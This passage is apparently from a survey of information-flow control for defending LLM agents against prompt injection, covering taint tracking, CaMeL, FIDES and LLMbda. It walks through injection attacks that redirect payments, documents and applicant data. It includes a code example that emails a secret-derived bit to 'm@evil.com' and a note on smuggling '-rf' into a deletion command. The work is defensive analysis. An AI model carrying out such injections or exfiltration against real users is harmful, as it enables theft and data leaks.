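Suppose a fairly careful tracker gives each value assigned inside a branch the label of the branch's condition as well as its own. The variables `b` and `c` start out public.

| | If `secret` is true | If `secret` is false |
|---|---|---|
| First `if` | The program skips it. `c` stays false and public. | The program runs it. `c` becomes true and secret. |
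| Second `if` | The program runs it. `b` becomes true. The condition, `c`, is public, so `b` is too. | The program skips it. `b` stays false and public. |
| Result | `b` is true and public | `b` is false and public |

In both runs, `b` ends up equal to `secret`, but its label is still "public". The tracker goes wrong when `secret` is true. In that case `c = true` does not run, which reveals the secret, but the tracker updates labels only for assignments that run. One pass through this code leaks one bit, and a program that repeats it for each bit can copy a whole password or account number.

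The problem is just as bad for integrity. If `secret` is replaced with a value from an email, and "public" with "trusted", the email's sender determines whether `b` is true, but the tracker labels `b` as trusted. If the program makes a payment when `b` is true, an outsider has authorised it.

Perl's taint mode misses an even simpler case. If a tainted value selects between two fixed strings, the result is not marked as tainted, and the manual says that marking it would make no sense. TaintDroid doesn't track implicit flows, and Enck and colleagues acknowledge that a malicious app could use them to evade tracking. This omission is easier to defend for programs that aren't malicious, because programmers seldom copy a whole secret this way by accident. But the problem is easy to overlook even in a careful design. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026)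 reports Fenton's leak in CaMeL, a system for isolating untrusted data in agents, fifty years after Denning's paper.

Denning described several remedies. In one, a compiler examines both branches before the program runs and inserts an instruction that raises the label of `c` after the first `if`, whether or not the branch was taken. In another, every variable's label is fixed in advance, and the machine refuses any assignment that breaks the rules. If `c` must remain public, the machine refuses `c = true` when `secret` is false. `c` then stays false in both runs, `b` becomes true in both, and the value of `b` reveals nothing about `secret`. Fenton proved that such run-time checks are sufficient when labels are fixed. However, the refusal has to remain hidden, since anyone who can read the error log could work out that `secret` was false.

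Denning and Denning's *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* avoids run-time refusals by moving the whole check into the compiler, which certifies a program only if no public result can depend on secret input. The check has to err on the side of rejection, so it rejects a program that sets `b` to 1 in both branches of a test on `secret`, even though the result is always the same. The check also requires the source code and a declared label for each variable, neither of which Enck and colleagues had for the apps they studied.

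### When everything is tainted

Catching more flows creates the opposite problem, because labels spread. TaintDroid's worst case was the IMSI, a number on the SIM card that identifies the subscriber. Its first digits are codes for the country and the network, and Android uses these codes as settings when it handles other data. Once the team marked the IMSI as private, the mark spread to entire messages and from there to a growing share of the phone's data. They had to turn this source off for their experiments. (They found apps leaking the IMSI anyway, because it travelled in the same messages as the phone number.)

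Some of the early systems that Denning reviewed never lowered a label, so once a process had read a secret file, everything it wrote afterwards counted as secret. Tracking implicit flows spreads labels further, because the tracker has to mark everything that either branch of a conditional might have changed. Enck and colleagues expected "rampant overtainting and false alerts" if anyone tried this on existing apps. Language models are an extreme case because any word a model writes may depend on anything earlier in its prompt. A cautious tracker therefore has to treat everything an agent writes after opening one email as untrusted.

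Practical systems therefore need a way to change labels deliberately. For secrecy, this is called *declassification*. A login page, for example, has to reveal whether a guess matched the secret password. For integrity, it is called *endorsement*. A user endorses the account number on an invoice, for example, by looking at it and confirming it. Endorsement replaces strict noninterference with the weaker guarantee that untrusted data can influence trusted outputs only at the points of endorsement. This guarantee is only as strong as the checks at those points.

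The usual way to make such exceptions was to declare some processes "trusted" and exempt them from the policy. Goguen and Meseguer considered it unnecessarily dangerous to leave any part of a system unrestricted, and wanted a precise policy for each exception. Garby and colleagues follow this advice in a programming language for agents. Changing a label requires an explicit `endorse` instruction, which an auditor can look for in the code. Garby and colleagues also prove that endorsing a value's integrity leaves the protection of secrets intact.

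An exception can be visible and still be wrong. Perl's manual offers a sample pattern that accepts letters, digits, underscores, hyphens, at signs and dots, because none of these has a special meaning to a command shell. But the pattern also accepts the text `-rf`. If a script passes that text to the Unix deletion command as a file name, the command treats it as an option to delete whole folders without asking. The check protects the shell but not the program that the shell starts. A single mark can't record this difference, because it shows only that the value has passed some check, not which one.

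The best endorsements test the property that matters at the sink. For a payment, that means looking up the account number in a trusted list of suppliers instead of checking that it consists of digits. Even then, a false invoice could send the money to the wrong supplier on the list.

### Which guarantees held

Researchers built complete systems on this theory, but few people outside research used them. Jif adds labels to the programming language Java and has the compiler check them. HiStar is an operating system that labels processes and controls what passes between them, and Flume brings similar controls to conventional operating systems. Enck and colleagues write that such systems were hard to apply to phones because languages with labels require careful development and often don't fit existing software, while operating systems that label whole processes can't follow private data inside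 an app. Perl's taint mode reached far more programmers because they could switch it on with one flag and add a few patterns. But according to a later edition of the manual on perldoc.jp, taint support slows down every Perl program, including those that don't use it, and since version 5.18 people have been able to build Perl without it.

Parameterised queries have the best record of all these mechanisms. Their guarantee depends on one component, the database's parser, and on programmers using them for every value. The remaining attacks mostly exploit queries built by joining strings, or parts of a query where a placeholder cannot go.

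The theorems about labels also held, but only under limited conditions. Denning excluded *covert channels*, in which a program signals indirectly, for example by changing how heavily it loads the machine. She also noted that a faulty compiler or faulty hardware could undo a correct certification. Implementations could also fail in simpler ways. ADEPT-50, an early time-sharing system with military-style security levels, raised a process's label as it opened files. But from the published description, Denning concluded that a process with top-secret clearance could write to any existing file with a lower label, whatever it had read before, so it could copy top-secret data into an unclassified file.

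Run-time trackers such as Perl's and TaintDroid did not guarantee protection against hostile programs, but they were good at catching careless ones, such as the fifteen apps that leaked locations. How well these results apply to agents depends on who writes the program. If an agent's plan is complete before it reads any email, the attacker supplies only data, as in Perl's threat model, and implicit flows arise only where non-malicious code branches on that data. Those branches still need checking, because an attacker can tailor the email to exploit them. If the model writes new code after reading the email, the attacker may influence that code, and a tracker that ignores implicit flows then offers little protection.

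## How do agent designs stop untrusted data from choosing actions?

Parameterised queries prevent injection because the database fixes what a command does before it receives any outside text. Agent designers want a similar order of events. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) argue in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, it must be impossible for that input to trigger a consequential action. They add that the agent's output should not leak data through an embedded link or pass instructions on to a later step. They think a general-purpose agent, which can use any tool for any task, is unlikely to meet this standard with the current kind of language model, so each of their designs rules some tasks out.

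### What an agent can give up

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe six patterns. One is the dual-LLM pattern, which needs a longer explanation below. The other five are:

- **Action selector.** The model translates a request into one of a fixed list of actions and never sees the results. A customer-service bot might choose between a link to the last order and a link to the password settings. Tool output can't inject anything because none of it reaches the model, but such an agent could never read an invoice.
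- **Plan, then execute.** The model commits to a list of tool calls before it reads any untrusted data. If the user wants today's schedule sent to their boss, the plan is to read the calendar and then email the boss's address. A planted calendar entry can't add a step or change the address, though it can rewrite the body of the email. The agent gives up changing course in response to what it reads.
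- **Map-reduce.** A separate, isolated model reads each document and returns something very restricted, such as yes or no to "is this an invoice?" Ordinary code or another model then combines the answers. A malicious file can at most get itself counted as an invoice, which the attacker could also have managed by planting a real one. The agent gives up free text from the documents.
- **Code, then execute.** The model writes a whole program instead of a list of steps. The program can call tools and can hand untrusted text to models that have none. Planted text can still change the contents of what the program sends.
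- **Context minimisation.** The system deletes the user's prompt once the model has turned it into, say, a database query. This protects against a malicious user, or one who has pasted in a stranger's text, but the model can no longer consult the original wording when it writes its answer.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues try these patterns on ten applications. The customer-service bot can use the simplest ones. Only the dual-LLM pattern fits the software-engineering agent, which has to read other people's code and documentation and then act.

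### Two models and a set of placeholders

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed splitting the agent into a planner, called the *privileged* model, and a *quarantined* model. The quarantined model's output is stored in a variable, such as `$email-summary-1`, and the privileged model receives only the variable's name. The privileged model can output an instruction to show the summary to the user, and ordinary software inserts the text only when it is displayed.

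An attacker can no longer choose the agent's actions but can still choose the values those actions use. Google DeepMind's paper on CaMeL, described below, points out this flaw with an example in which a user asks the agent to send Bob a document he requested at the last meeting. Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The privileged model correctly plans to find the notes, extract the name and address, fetch the document and send it. But if somebody has planted an instruction in the notes, the quarantined model may return the attacker's address, and the agent then sends the document there. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, acknowledges that he had not noticed this flaw.

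*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) names two properties. *Control-flow integrity* means that only the planner determines which calls run, in what order and under what conditions. *Data-flow security* means that untrusted data can't manipulate the arguments of those calls or the values that determine which branch runs. Splitting the agent into two models provides only control-flow integrity.

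Information-flow control is the natural way to deal with the rest. Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao built an early system of this kind, *f*-secure, in 2024. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes how an isolated planner in *f*-secure produced structured plans from trusted data, and untrusted components carried out and refined them. *f*-secure came with a formal model and a proof, but the 2025 paper objects that the implementation still let untrusted data affect plans through implicit flows.

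### CaMeL: a program whose values carry labels

Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues published CaMeL in 2025 in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. The name is short for "capabilities for machine learning". It handles a request in four stages, which Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe in detail:

1. The planner model receives the user's request and writes a program for the whole task in a restricted version of Python. It has seen no untrusted data at this point.
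2. Wherever the task needs a fact from untrusted text, the program calls a quarantined model and states what type of answer it expects, such as an email address.
3. An interpreter runs the program, makes the tool calls and attaches a *capability* to every value. This is a label that records the value's sources and the people who may read it. A value computed from other values inherits their labels.
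4. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy. This is a short Python function that receives the call, its arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason.

The restrictions on Python make the labels easier to track. There are no open-ended `while` loops, for example, and the interpreter runs the program one operation at a time, so it can record which variables were used to compute each new one. In Willison's example, the agent looks up Bob's address in the user's latest email and sends Bob a reminder. Because the address comes from the email, the interpreter treats it as untrusted too. The policy can allow the message if the user already trusts the address and require approval otherwise.

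According to *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026), the fixed program guarantees that untrusted data can affect which existing branch runs but cannot add a new one. If the program pays invoices under $1,000 and asks the user about larger ones, whoever writes the invoice can choose between paying and asking, but cannot make the agent forward mail, because no branch does that. However, the planner gets another try when a program fails. Garby and colleagues note that CaMeL censors the error messages the planner sees, to keep untrusted text out of the next version.

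The separation also improves privacy. The planner never sees the user's mail, so the company that hosts the planner doesn't either. Finding an address in an email is easier than writing the program, so a smaller model can do it, perhaps on the user's own computer.

CaMeL checks each call against its policies when the program reaches that call. Nikolaou and colleagues built CaMeLoT to check the whole program before it starts. One of their rules forbids any payment whose recipient or amount depends on untrusted data. A program that paid an emailed invoice would break this rule, so CaMeLoT would reject it and return the reason to the planner, which could then try again. Rules can also cover a whole run, for example by requiring the agent to close every incident ticket it opens. The check has to allow for any number of passes through a loop, so it sometimes rejects programs that would have been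 safe.

### FIDES: labels around an ordinary agent loop

FIDES, a system from Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, keeps the usual loop, in which a planner model chooses one tool call, gets a result and chooses the next. It attaches a two-part label to every message, tool result and variable. The integrity part is either *trusted* or *untrusted*, and the confidentiality part is the set of people who may read the data. Combined data is untrusted if any piece is, and only people who may read every piece may read the combination.

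Microsoft's *Information-flow control* has an example of the confidentiality part. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't supposed to know the figures yet, has asked about them. After the agent has read both emails, anything it writes has the readers

{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex},

so the agent may not reply to Marco without asking. Nobody has attacked anything here. The same rule prevents ordinary indiscretion.

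FIDES also keeps a label for the *context*, meaning everything that the planner has read so far. As in Biba's model, reading a single email would make the context untrusted and block the rest of the task. FIDES avoids this by hiding data. It compares each part of a tool result with the context's label, and puts any part that would make the context less trusted or more secret into a variable. The planner sees the variable's name and whatever is left. It might see when an email arrived but not what it says. (The original dual-LLM pattern hides everything the quarantined model handles, including harmless parts that might have helped the planner.)

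The planner can use a hidden variable in three ways:

- It can pass the variable to a tool without reading it.
- It can put a question about the variable to a quarantined model. The answer goes into a new variable that inherits the old one's label.
- It can *inspect* the variable, which puts the contents into the context and changes the context's label accordingly.

Inspecting untrusted content is less risky when the content can carry very little information, so FIDES can add a data type to the label. A yes-or-no answer conveys at most one bit, and a choice from a list of *n* options at most log₂ *n* bits, whereas free text has no such limit. *Constrained decoding* enforces the type by allowing the quarantined model to generate only text that fits it. Suppose a user wants a calendar event created if any of their latest three emails proposes a meeting. The planner asks the quarantined model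 for a yes or no and inspects the answer. If it is yes, the planner has the details extracted into a variable and passes the variable to the calendar tool without reading it. A stranger could get a bogus event into the calendar but couldn't make the agent do anything else. Letting the planner act on the answer is a form of endorsement, which the policy has to permit explicitly.

FIDES checks a policy before every tool call. Costa and colleagues give two basic rules. The integrity rule allows a consequential call only if the call and all its arguments are trusted. The confidentiality rule allows data to be sent out only if every recipient is permitted to read it. A call and its arguments have separate labels. The call takes the label of the context in which the planner chose it, while a hidden variable passed as an argument keeps its own label. A trusted call can therefore have untrusted arguments,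 and the designer must decide for each tool whether to allow that.

### Planning everything or choosing each step

CaMeL and FIDES can both handle simple conditions. If the user wants to book a hotel only when its rating is above 4, CaMeL's planner writes an `if` statement, and FIDES's planner checks a yes-or-no answer before booking. FIDES handles unexpected trusted results better because its planner can read them and adapt, whereas CaMeL's program must already include code for that case.

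Foerster and colleagues measured how much planning ahead this takes. CaMeL's programs for AgentDojo average 52 lines, with about five tool calls and four branches. They adapted CaMeL to an agent that operates a computer through its screen, where a cookie notice or a login page can appear at any time. Those programs averaged 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, and about half of each program was fallbacks that a given run never used. More branches also give an attacker more paths to trigger, for instance by drawing a fake cookie notice.

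Neither CaMeL nor FIDES can safely carry out a request like "do the tasks on my to-do list" if outsiders can write on the list. CaMeL's planner can't write the program without knowing the tasks. FIDES's planner can read them, but doing so makes its context untrusted, so the integrity rule blocks any consequential task on the list. Foerster and colleagues regard this as a fundamental limit of both designs, because the untrusted data contains the sequence of actions the agent is supposed to take.

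CaMeL and FIDES also fail differently when misconfigured. CaMeL's planner never reads tool output, so if a policy is missing, an injection can affect the values in the program but not its steps. FIDES's planner can read a malicious email, and without policies nothing would then stop it from following the email's instructions.

### The invoice, label by label

For the request to find the invoice and pay it, CaMeL's planner might write:

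```
email   = find_email("invoice")
account = ask_quarantined("Which account is to be paid?", email)
amount  = ask_quarantined("How much is due?", email)
send_money(recipient=account, amount=amount)
```

FIDES would probably make the same calls, one at a time. The table shows the labels at each call, assuming an email's readers are its sender and recipients.

| Step | CaMeL | FIDES |
|---|---|---|
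| The user makes the request | The planner writes the whole program. Text that it writes itself, such as "invoice", is trusted. | The context is trusted. |
| Find the email | `email` gets the sender as a source, with the user and the sender as readers. | The body goes into a variable labelled untrusted, with the same readers. The context stays trusted. |
| Extract the account and the amount | `account` and `amount` inherit the label of `email`. | Both answers go into new untrusted variables. The context stays trusted. |
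| Pay | The policy receives an untrusted recipient and an untrusted amount. | The policy receives a trusted call with two untrusted arguments. |

Attack A fails against CaMeL because the program has no step for forwarding mail to the stranger. FIDES's planner could choose to inspect the malicious email and might then try to obey it, but the context would be untrusted by then. Costa and colleagues tested a rule that allows an email to be sent if its recipients are already allowed to read the contents, or if the planner chose the call in a trusted context. FIDES blocks the call because the stranger isn't allowed to read the user's other mail and the context is untrusted.

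A cleverer attacker would address the quarantined model instead, telling it to return the attacker's account number. Attack A then has the same result as attack B, because an instruction in the email and a false number on the invoice both put a wrong value in `account`, with the same label.

The outcome then depends entirely on the payment policy. If CaMeL's policy requires a trusted recipient, the interpreter stops and can ask the user, who has to notice that the number is wrong. In FIDES, the integrity rule as stated above would block the payment because its arguments are untrusted. But on AgentDojo's payment tool, Costa and colleagues tested a more lenient rule that checks only the label of the call. Under that rule, FIDES would pay the thief, because the planner chose the call in a trusted context. They acknowledge that their test policies ignore arguments. The strict rule, however, would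 also block payment of every genuine emailed invoice.

A trusted list of suppliers allows a better policy in either system. The quarantined model only picks which supplier on the list sent the invoice, and ordinary code looks up that supplier's account. The policy must allow a choice based on an untrusted email, which is reasonable when the list is short and every supplier on it is legitimate. The amount still needs a limit or a human check.

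### What AgentDojo has tested

With OpenAI's o3 model, CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and no attack within its threat model succeeded. Narisetty and colleagues report these figures from the CaMeL paper. AgentDojo's scoring did count two attacks as successful, and Garby and colleagues explain both. In one, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The CaMeL paper places this case outside its threat model because the user had told the agent to do whatever the file said. In the other attack, the agent quoted hotel reviews that contained the attacker's text.

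The hotel case is a scoring flaw that also affects other systems. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) describes it for a system called TACIT. The user asked to book one hotel, and the attacker had planted praise for another in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel and showed the user the reviews, but AgentDojo counted this as a successful attack because the other hotel's name appeared in the answer. The file case is harder to dismiss as a scoring flaw because the money goes to the attacker.

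Other researchers have since tested CaMeL and found similar security. In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded. *Kairos* (2026) tested CaMeL with its policies on, using two different models. The average attack success rate over the four applications was 0.2% with one model (roughly one successful attack among the 105 Slack pairs) and 0.4% with the other (roughly two among the 140 travel pairs). CaMeL completed far fewer of the users' tasks in these tests than in the original one.

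Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on the banking tasks with its policies on and off, which helps separate the effect of the fixed program from the effect of the policies. The table counts the runs that finished.

| Model | Attacks that succeeded, policies off | Policies on |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 1 of 240 | 0 of 231 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | 4 of 382 | 0 of 357 |

The fixed program provided nearly all the protection. In 97 of the 144 pairs of user task and attack in AgentDojo's banking suite, the attacker needs a tool call that a program for the user's task would never contain, so those attacks ought to fail even without a policy. A low attack success rate on AgentDojo is therefore weak evidence that a system's policies work.

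Two of the five successful attacks came from this supposedly safe group. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. The planner had no access to the file's contents, so it wrote a loop with a branch for every tool, and the file's contents determined which branches ran. The program never changed, so control-flow integrity formally held, but the attacker could choose any action. CaMeL blocked these attacks when its policies were on.

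Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o, using an attack template whose author knows the agent's tools and spells out the calls to make. After removing cases they considered misjudged, they counted 152 successful attacks against an ordinary agent. With FIDES's policies off, 21 attacks still succeeded because the planner could inspect malicious text and obey it. No attacks succeeded against a simpler version whose planner can't read hidden variables, even without policies, but it completed far fewer tasks that require reading. With policies on, no attack succeeded against FIDES. The tested version didn't use constrained decoding, which they found unnecessary for most AgentDojo tasks.

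AgentDojo's unadjusted count of successful attacks on FIDES with policies on was three, all in Slack. Costa and colleagues discount such cases for several reasons. One Slack attack counts as successful as soon as the agent calls the tool for inviting a new member, even if the policy then blocks the call. Their policy also deliberately allows some actions that the attacker wants, such as sending a message without links to a channel whose members may all read its contents. Discounting blocked calls is clearly right. But if permitted actions are discounted too, "no successful attacks" partly means that no attack broke the policy, and a user might still be unhappy to find a stranger's message posted under their name.

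Costa and colleagues also assigned labels in a way that favours FIDES. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, so every planted instruction arrived with the right label. A real deployment has no such list of attacks. In one banking task, the user wanted their password changed if the agent found a suspicious transaction. Transaction amounts counted as trusted, so the planner had access to them. It treated a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without reading the untrusted description. This broke no rule, but anyone who sends the user money chooses the amount and so could influence that decision.

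Narisetty and colleagues warn that nearly all these results come from fixed sets of attacks, as did the early results for detectors that later failed. The warning applies less to the choice of steps than to the data those steps use. If the interpreter works correctly, no email can add a step to a program that the planner has already written. But AgentDojo's attacks tell an agent to call tools, so they are a poor test of a quarantined model, which has no tools. Text designed to produce a false account number would test the payment policy much harder, and a FIDES policy that ignores arguments would not stop it.

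### When one agent instructs another

Both designs assume that the user's request is trustworthy, an assumption that can fail when the "user" is another agent. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents running GPT-5.2. A coordinating agent received a request to send Julie a Slack summary of all job applicants and got the data from a database agent. The database contained a planted instruction to email the data to an outsider. Both agents correctly treated the instruction as data. But the coordinating agent then put a summary containing the instruction into its request to the notification agent, whose planner treated the whole request as coming from its user and added a step that sent the email.

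A rule that recipients must be trusted would probably not have helped, because the outsider's address had lost its label and looked like part of the user's request. Peters-Gill and colleagues propose sending instructions and data through separate channels and keeping the labels attached. On a multi-agent extension of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent separately, and 0.0% with the separate channels.

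### From research systems to products

In May 2026, Microsoft added FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents, as an experimental, opt-in feature. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) explains the set-up with an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. The developer labels the data each tool returns and specifies what data each tool accepts. For example, the developer labels bug reports as untrusted and bars the tool that changes files from running in an untrusted context. By default, the framework hides untrusted text from the main model. When a call breaks a rule, the framework either blocks it or asks a person to approve it.

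The main weakness is that results from unlabelled tools count as trusted and public by default. A developer who forgets to label the inbox tool gets no protection against malicious email and no warning that the protection is missing. Microsoft has asked developers whether it should reverse this default. That would be safer, but each unlabelled tool would then make the context untrusted and block later steps, so developers would have to label their tools before their agents worked properly.

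GitHub's command-line coding agent, Copilot CLI, has experimental support for labelling the data it reads. According to Microsoft, the agent keeps a single label for everything it has read, which is cruder than labelling each value. The labels come from GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools. The server can mark content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private repositories as private and trusted.

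These two labels are enough to stop an attack that researchers had demonstrated earlier, in which a stranger uses a bug report in a public repository to tell the agent to copy private code into a public comment. Once the agent has read both the report and the code, its context is labeled untrusted and private, so the rule forbids it from posting publicly. The labels would not stop an instruction that an employee had pasted from a public website into a private repository, because everything in that repository counts as trusted.

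When Microsoft described it, Copilot CLI enforced rules for only some of the GitHub server's tools and for no other servers. Microsoft has released a gateway that adds labels for servers that don't provide them. For each tool, someone still has to specify its result format, write a function that carries labels from its inputs to its outputs, and write or choose a policy.

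## What has been proved about these designs, and on what assumptions?

The tests of CaMeL and FIDES used fixed sets of attacks, so they can't establish a guarantee, which requires a proof. Researchers have proved several properties of systems like these, but some are much weaker than others, and all rest on assumptions that may not hold in deployment.

### FIDES and explicit secrecy

Costa and colleagues prove that the label tracking in FIDES can enforce *explicit secrecy*. Roughly, this means that no secret ends up in public data by copying or calculation, although a secret may still influence what the agent decides to do. For the exact version, take any sequence of steps that the agent might go through. Let *g* be the combined effect of its tool calls on the stored data, so that a store *d* becomes *g*(*d*), and write *d*₁ ≈ *d*₂ if two stores contain the same public data. Explicit secrecy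 requires, for every such sequence, that

if *d*₁ ≈ *d*₂, then *g*(*d*₁) ≈ *g*(*d*₂).

A program that posts "yes" if a secret is true and "no" if it is false meets this definition, because each of its two paths posts the same word whatever the store contains. Anyone who reads the post still learns the secret, because the secret determined which path ran. By design, FIDES does not track such implicit flows. Its confidentiality rule would often block this post, since anything the planner writes after reading a secret counts as secret. But an outsider who can see which tools the agent calls, and in what order, may still infer something about the secret. The model also excludes timing and the length of network messages.

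Costa and colleagues consider full noninterference too restrictive. They think it would essentially bar an agent from calling any tool that might change public data once it had called one that might read secrets. They therefore settle for a weaker guarantee, as TaintDroid did on phones.

The loop checks the policy before every tool call, so a call that breaks the policy can't run, whatever the model writes. This property is simpler and matters more against injections.

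The theorem covers only the kind of agent loop that FIDES uses. It holds for any tools, but a developer who restructured the loop would need a new proof. The proof also assumes that the model always gives the same reply to the same conversation, whereas deployed models usually generate text partly at random.

### What CaMeL's tracking misses

CaMeL has no comparable theorem. Its planner writes a new program for each request, so a proof would have to cover every program it might write. According to Garby and colleagues, the CaMeL paper calls formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work.

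Some leaks escape CaMeL's labels through *side channels*, which are by-products of a computation that an outsider can observe. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, describe three. If a program fetches a web page as many times as a secret number indicates, the site's owner can learn the number by counting visits in the access log, even though no single request contains it. If an error occurs only when a secret meets some condition, whether the error occurs reveals one bit. A program's running time can also depend on a secret. Tallam and Miller base their argument on attacks on other systems and don't demonstrate these leaks on CaMeL, but the loop would be easy to exploit. They suggest capping the number of repetitions, returning errors as ordinary values, and padding sensitive operations so they always take the same time.

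Garby and colleagues found two gaps in CaMeL's tracking itself. The first is Fenton's leak, which arises because CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch that the program takes. The following program, adapted from their example, tells a stranger whether the user is rich:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
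```

When the balance is above the threshold, the program skips `rich = False`, so `rich` stays true with a public label and CaMeL allows the email. When the balance is lower, no email goes out. An attacker can't insert this code directly, because CaMeL's planner writes the program before reading any untrusted data. The gap still matters if an honest program branches this way or if the user's request contains an attacker's text.

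The second gap is in the loop that prompts the planner for a new program when the last one fails. This loop is ordinary Python code that runs outside CaMeL's interpreter and doesn't track labels. Whether a policy blocked a program can depend on a secret, so each run can leak one bit. Most information-flow systems allow a leak of one bit per run. But each new attempt in CaMeL starts with clean labels, so an attacker who controls the attempts can extract a different bit each time until they have the whole secret. A 16-digit account number would take at most 54 runs.

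A third flaw, which Garby and colleagues mention in a footnote, is that inserting an untrusted value into a text template makes the result trusted. It may be the most worrying of the three in practice, because programs routinely build messages from templates.

### Labels on conversations

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda to rule out such flaws altogether. It is a *lambda calculus*, a minimal programming language made of functions, with added instructions for calling a language model. In the simplest version, a value's label can contain U for untrusted, S for secret, both or neither. A result's label combines the labels of everything used to compute it. The interpreter also keeps a label for the decisions that led to the current point in the program, and adds it to whatever the program computes there.

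The conversation with the model has a label too, which combines the labels of all the messages sent so far. If a program sends the model a stranger's email, the conversation becomes untrusted, and so does every later reply. Two instructions keep this under control. `fork` runs part of a program in a temporary copy of the conversation and afterwards restores the original. `clear` empties the conversation. In simplified notation, with `ask` for sending a prompt and reading the reply, a program can extract an account number like this:

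```
account = fork( clear; ask("Which account is to be paid? " + email) )
```

The program copies the conversation, empties the copy and runs its query there. The answer comes back with the label U, but the main conversation is still trusted because it never contained the email. This one line serves the same purpose as the quarantined model in CaMeL and FIDES, but programmers can use it wherever they need isolation, instead of relying on a fixed part of the system's architecture.

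A model's reply may also be code, which inherits the conversation's label when the interpreter runs it. If a malicious email causes the model to reply with code that sends money, that code runs as untrusted, and a payment tool that requires a trusted recipient rejects it.

Fenton's leak could also occur in conversations. Suppose a program adds a message to a public conversation only if a secret is true. If the interpreter raised the conversation's label then, the label would still be public in runs where the secret was false. To prevent this leak, the interpreter stops the run instead of raising the label.

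### Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference

The main theorem applies to every program in LLMbda, including agents that write and run their own code. Take an agent with fixed trusted inputs. Let *P*ₓ(*r*) be the probability that it finishes with the trusted result *r* when the untrusted data is *x*. Then for any two versions of the untrusted data, *x* and *x*′,

Σᵣ max(*P*ₓ(*r*), *P*ₓ′(*r*)) ≤ 1.

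This form of the condition is equivalent to the one Garby and colleagues give. To illustrate it with invented numbers, suppose an agent either pays a supplier or asks the user, and both results carry trusted labels.

| Outcome | Email 1 | Email 2 | Email 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pays the supplier | 0.60 | 0.50 | 0.30 |
| Asks the user | 0.30 | 0.30 | 0.70 |
| Stops without a result | 0.10 | 0.20 | 0.00 |

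For emails 1 and 2, the larger probabilities in the first two rows are 0.60 and 0.30, which add up to 0.90. The theorem allows this difference because email 2 has only turned some payments into stopped runs. For emails 1 and 3, the sum is 0.60 + 0.70 = 1.30. The theorem rules out this difference because email 3 has turned payments into questions.

*Noninterference* is the classical idea that changing the untrusted data can't change the trusted results. Here it is *probabilistic* because a language model's replies are random. Two runs can differ even with the same email, so the condition compares the probabilities of results. *Termination-insensitive* means that untrusted data may affect whether the agent finishes. If a failed label check stops a run, that run counts as unfinished, so an attacker may still be able to prevent a payment, or to signal something by whether the payment happens.

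If the agent always finishes, the condition requires the two sets of probabilities to be equal. Otherwise, the statistical distance between them is at most the average of the two stopping probabilities, which is 0.15 for emails 1 and 2. Garby and colleagues first tried a definition that compared only finished runs, but it was wrong. If an email stopped half of the runs that would otherwise end in a question, payments would make up a larger share of the finished runs even though no payment had become more likely.

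The proof uses an imaginary second interpreter that skips any computation once its label becomes untrusted and substitutes an empty value. Because this interpreter never reads untrusted data, it gives the same probabilities for every email. It also produces each trusted result at least as often as the real interpreter, because it can't get stuck in the parts it skips. Its probabilities are therefore upper limits on the real interpreter's probabilities for both emails, and they add up to at most 1. The same argument works for secrets, with "secret" in place of "untrusted" and "public" in place of "trusted".

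### Endorsement and the checked interpreter

Under this theorem, an agent could never send money to an account number taken from an email if the payment tool requires a trusted number. LLMbda's `endorse` instruction makes an exception by removing a value's untrusted mark. A second theorem, the *insulated* version, covers programs that use `endorse`. In this theorem, every label has an integrity part and a confidentiality part, and changes to the integrity part don't weaken the protection of secrets. Even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted data and the program endorses all of it, secrets can't reach public results except through whether the run finishes.

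The insulated theorem does not guarantee integrity once a program endorses a value. As in FIDES, an outsider's influence then depends on how much information that value can carry.

Garby and colleagues wrote the language, the theorems and the interpreter in Lean, which lets a computer check each step of a proof. They believe theirs is the first program for running language-model agents to have machine-checked security theorems about its own executable code. The rules for CaMeL's labels, by contrast, exist only as Python code, which is hard to audit.

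The proof treats the model, which the program calls over the internet, as a book of answers with one entry for each combination of call number and conversation. With a fixed book, the interpreter is an ordinary deterministic function. The proof shows that if the book is drawn at random from the model's own probabilities, the interpreter's results have exactly the probabilities that the noninterference theorem describes. It doesn't cover the network call itself, and it assumes that a reply depends only on the conversation sent. If a provider carried memories from one conversation to the next, this assumption would fail and `clear` would no longer erase the email.

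### Two successful attacks on a proved system

Garby and colleagues built an agent in LLMbda, called Randori, and tested it on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Randori avoids CaMeL's retry problem by testing its programs on made-up data first. It can rewrite a failed program repeatedly, up to a limit, and only the final version runs on the real account. Two attacks succeeded in 1,296 attacked runs, which covered three models and 144 pairs of task and attack, with three runs of each.

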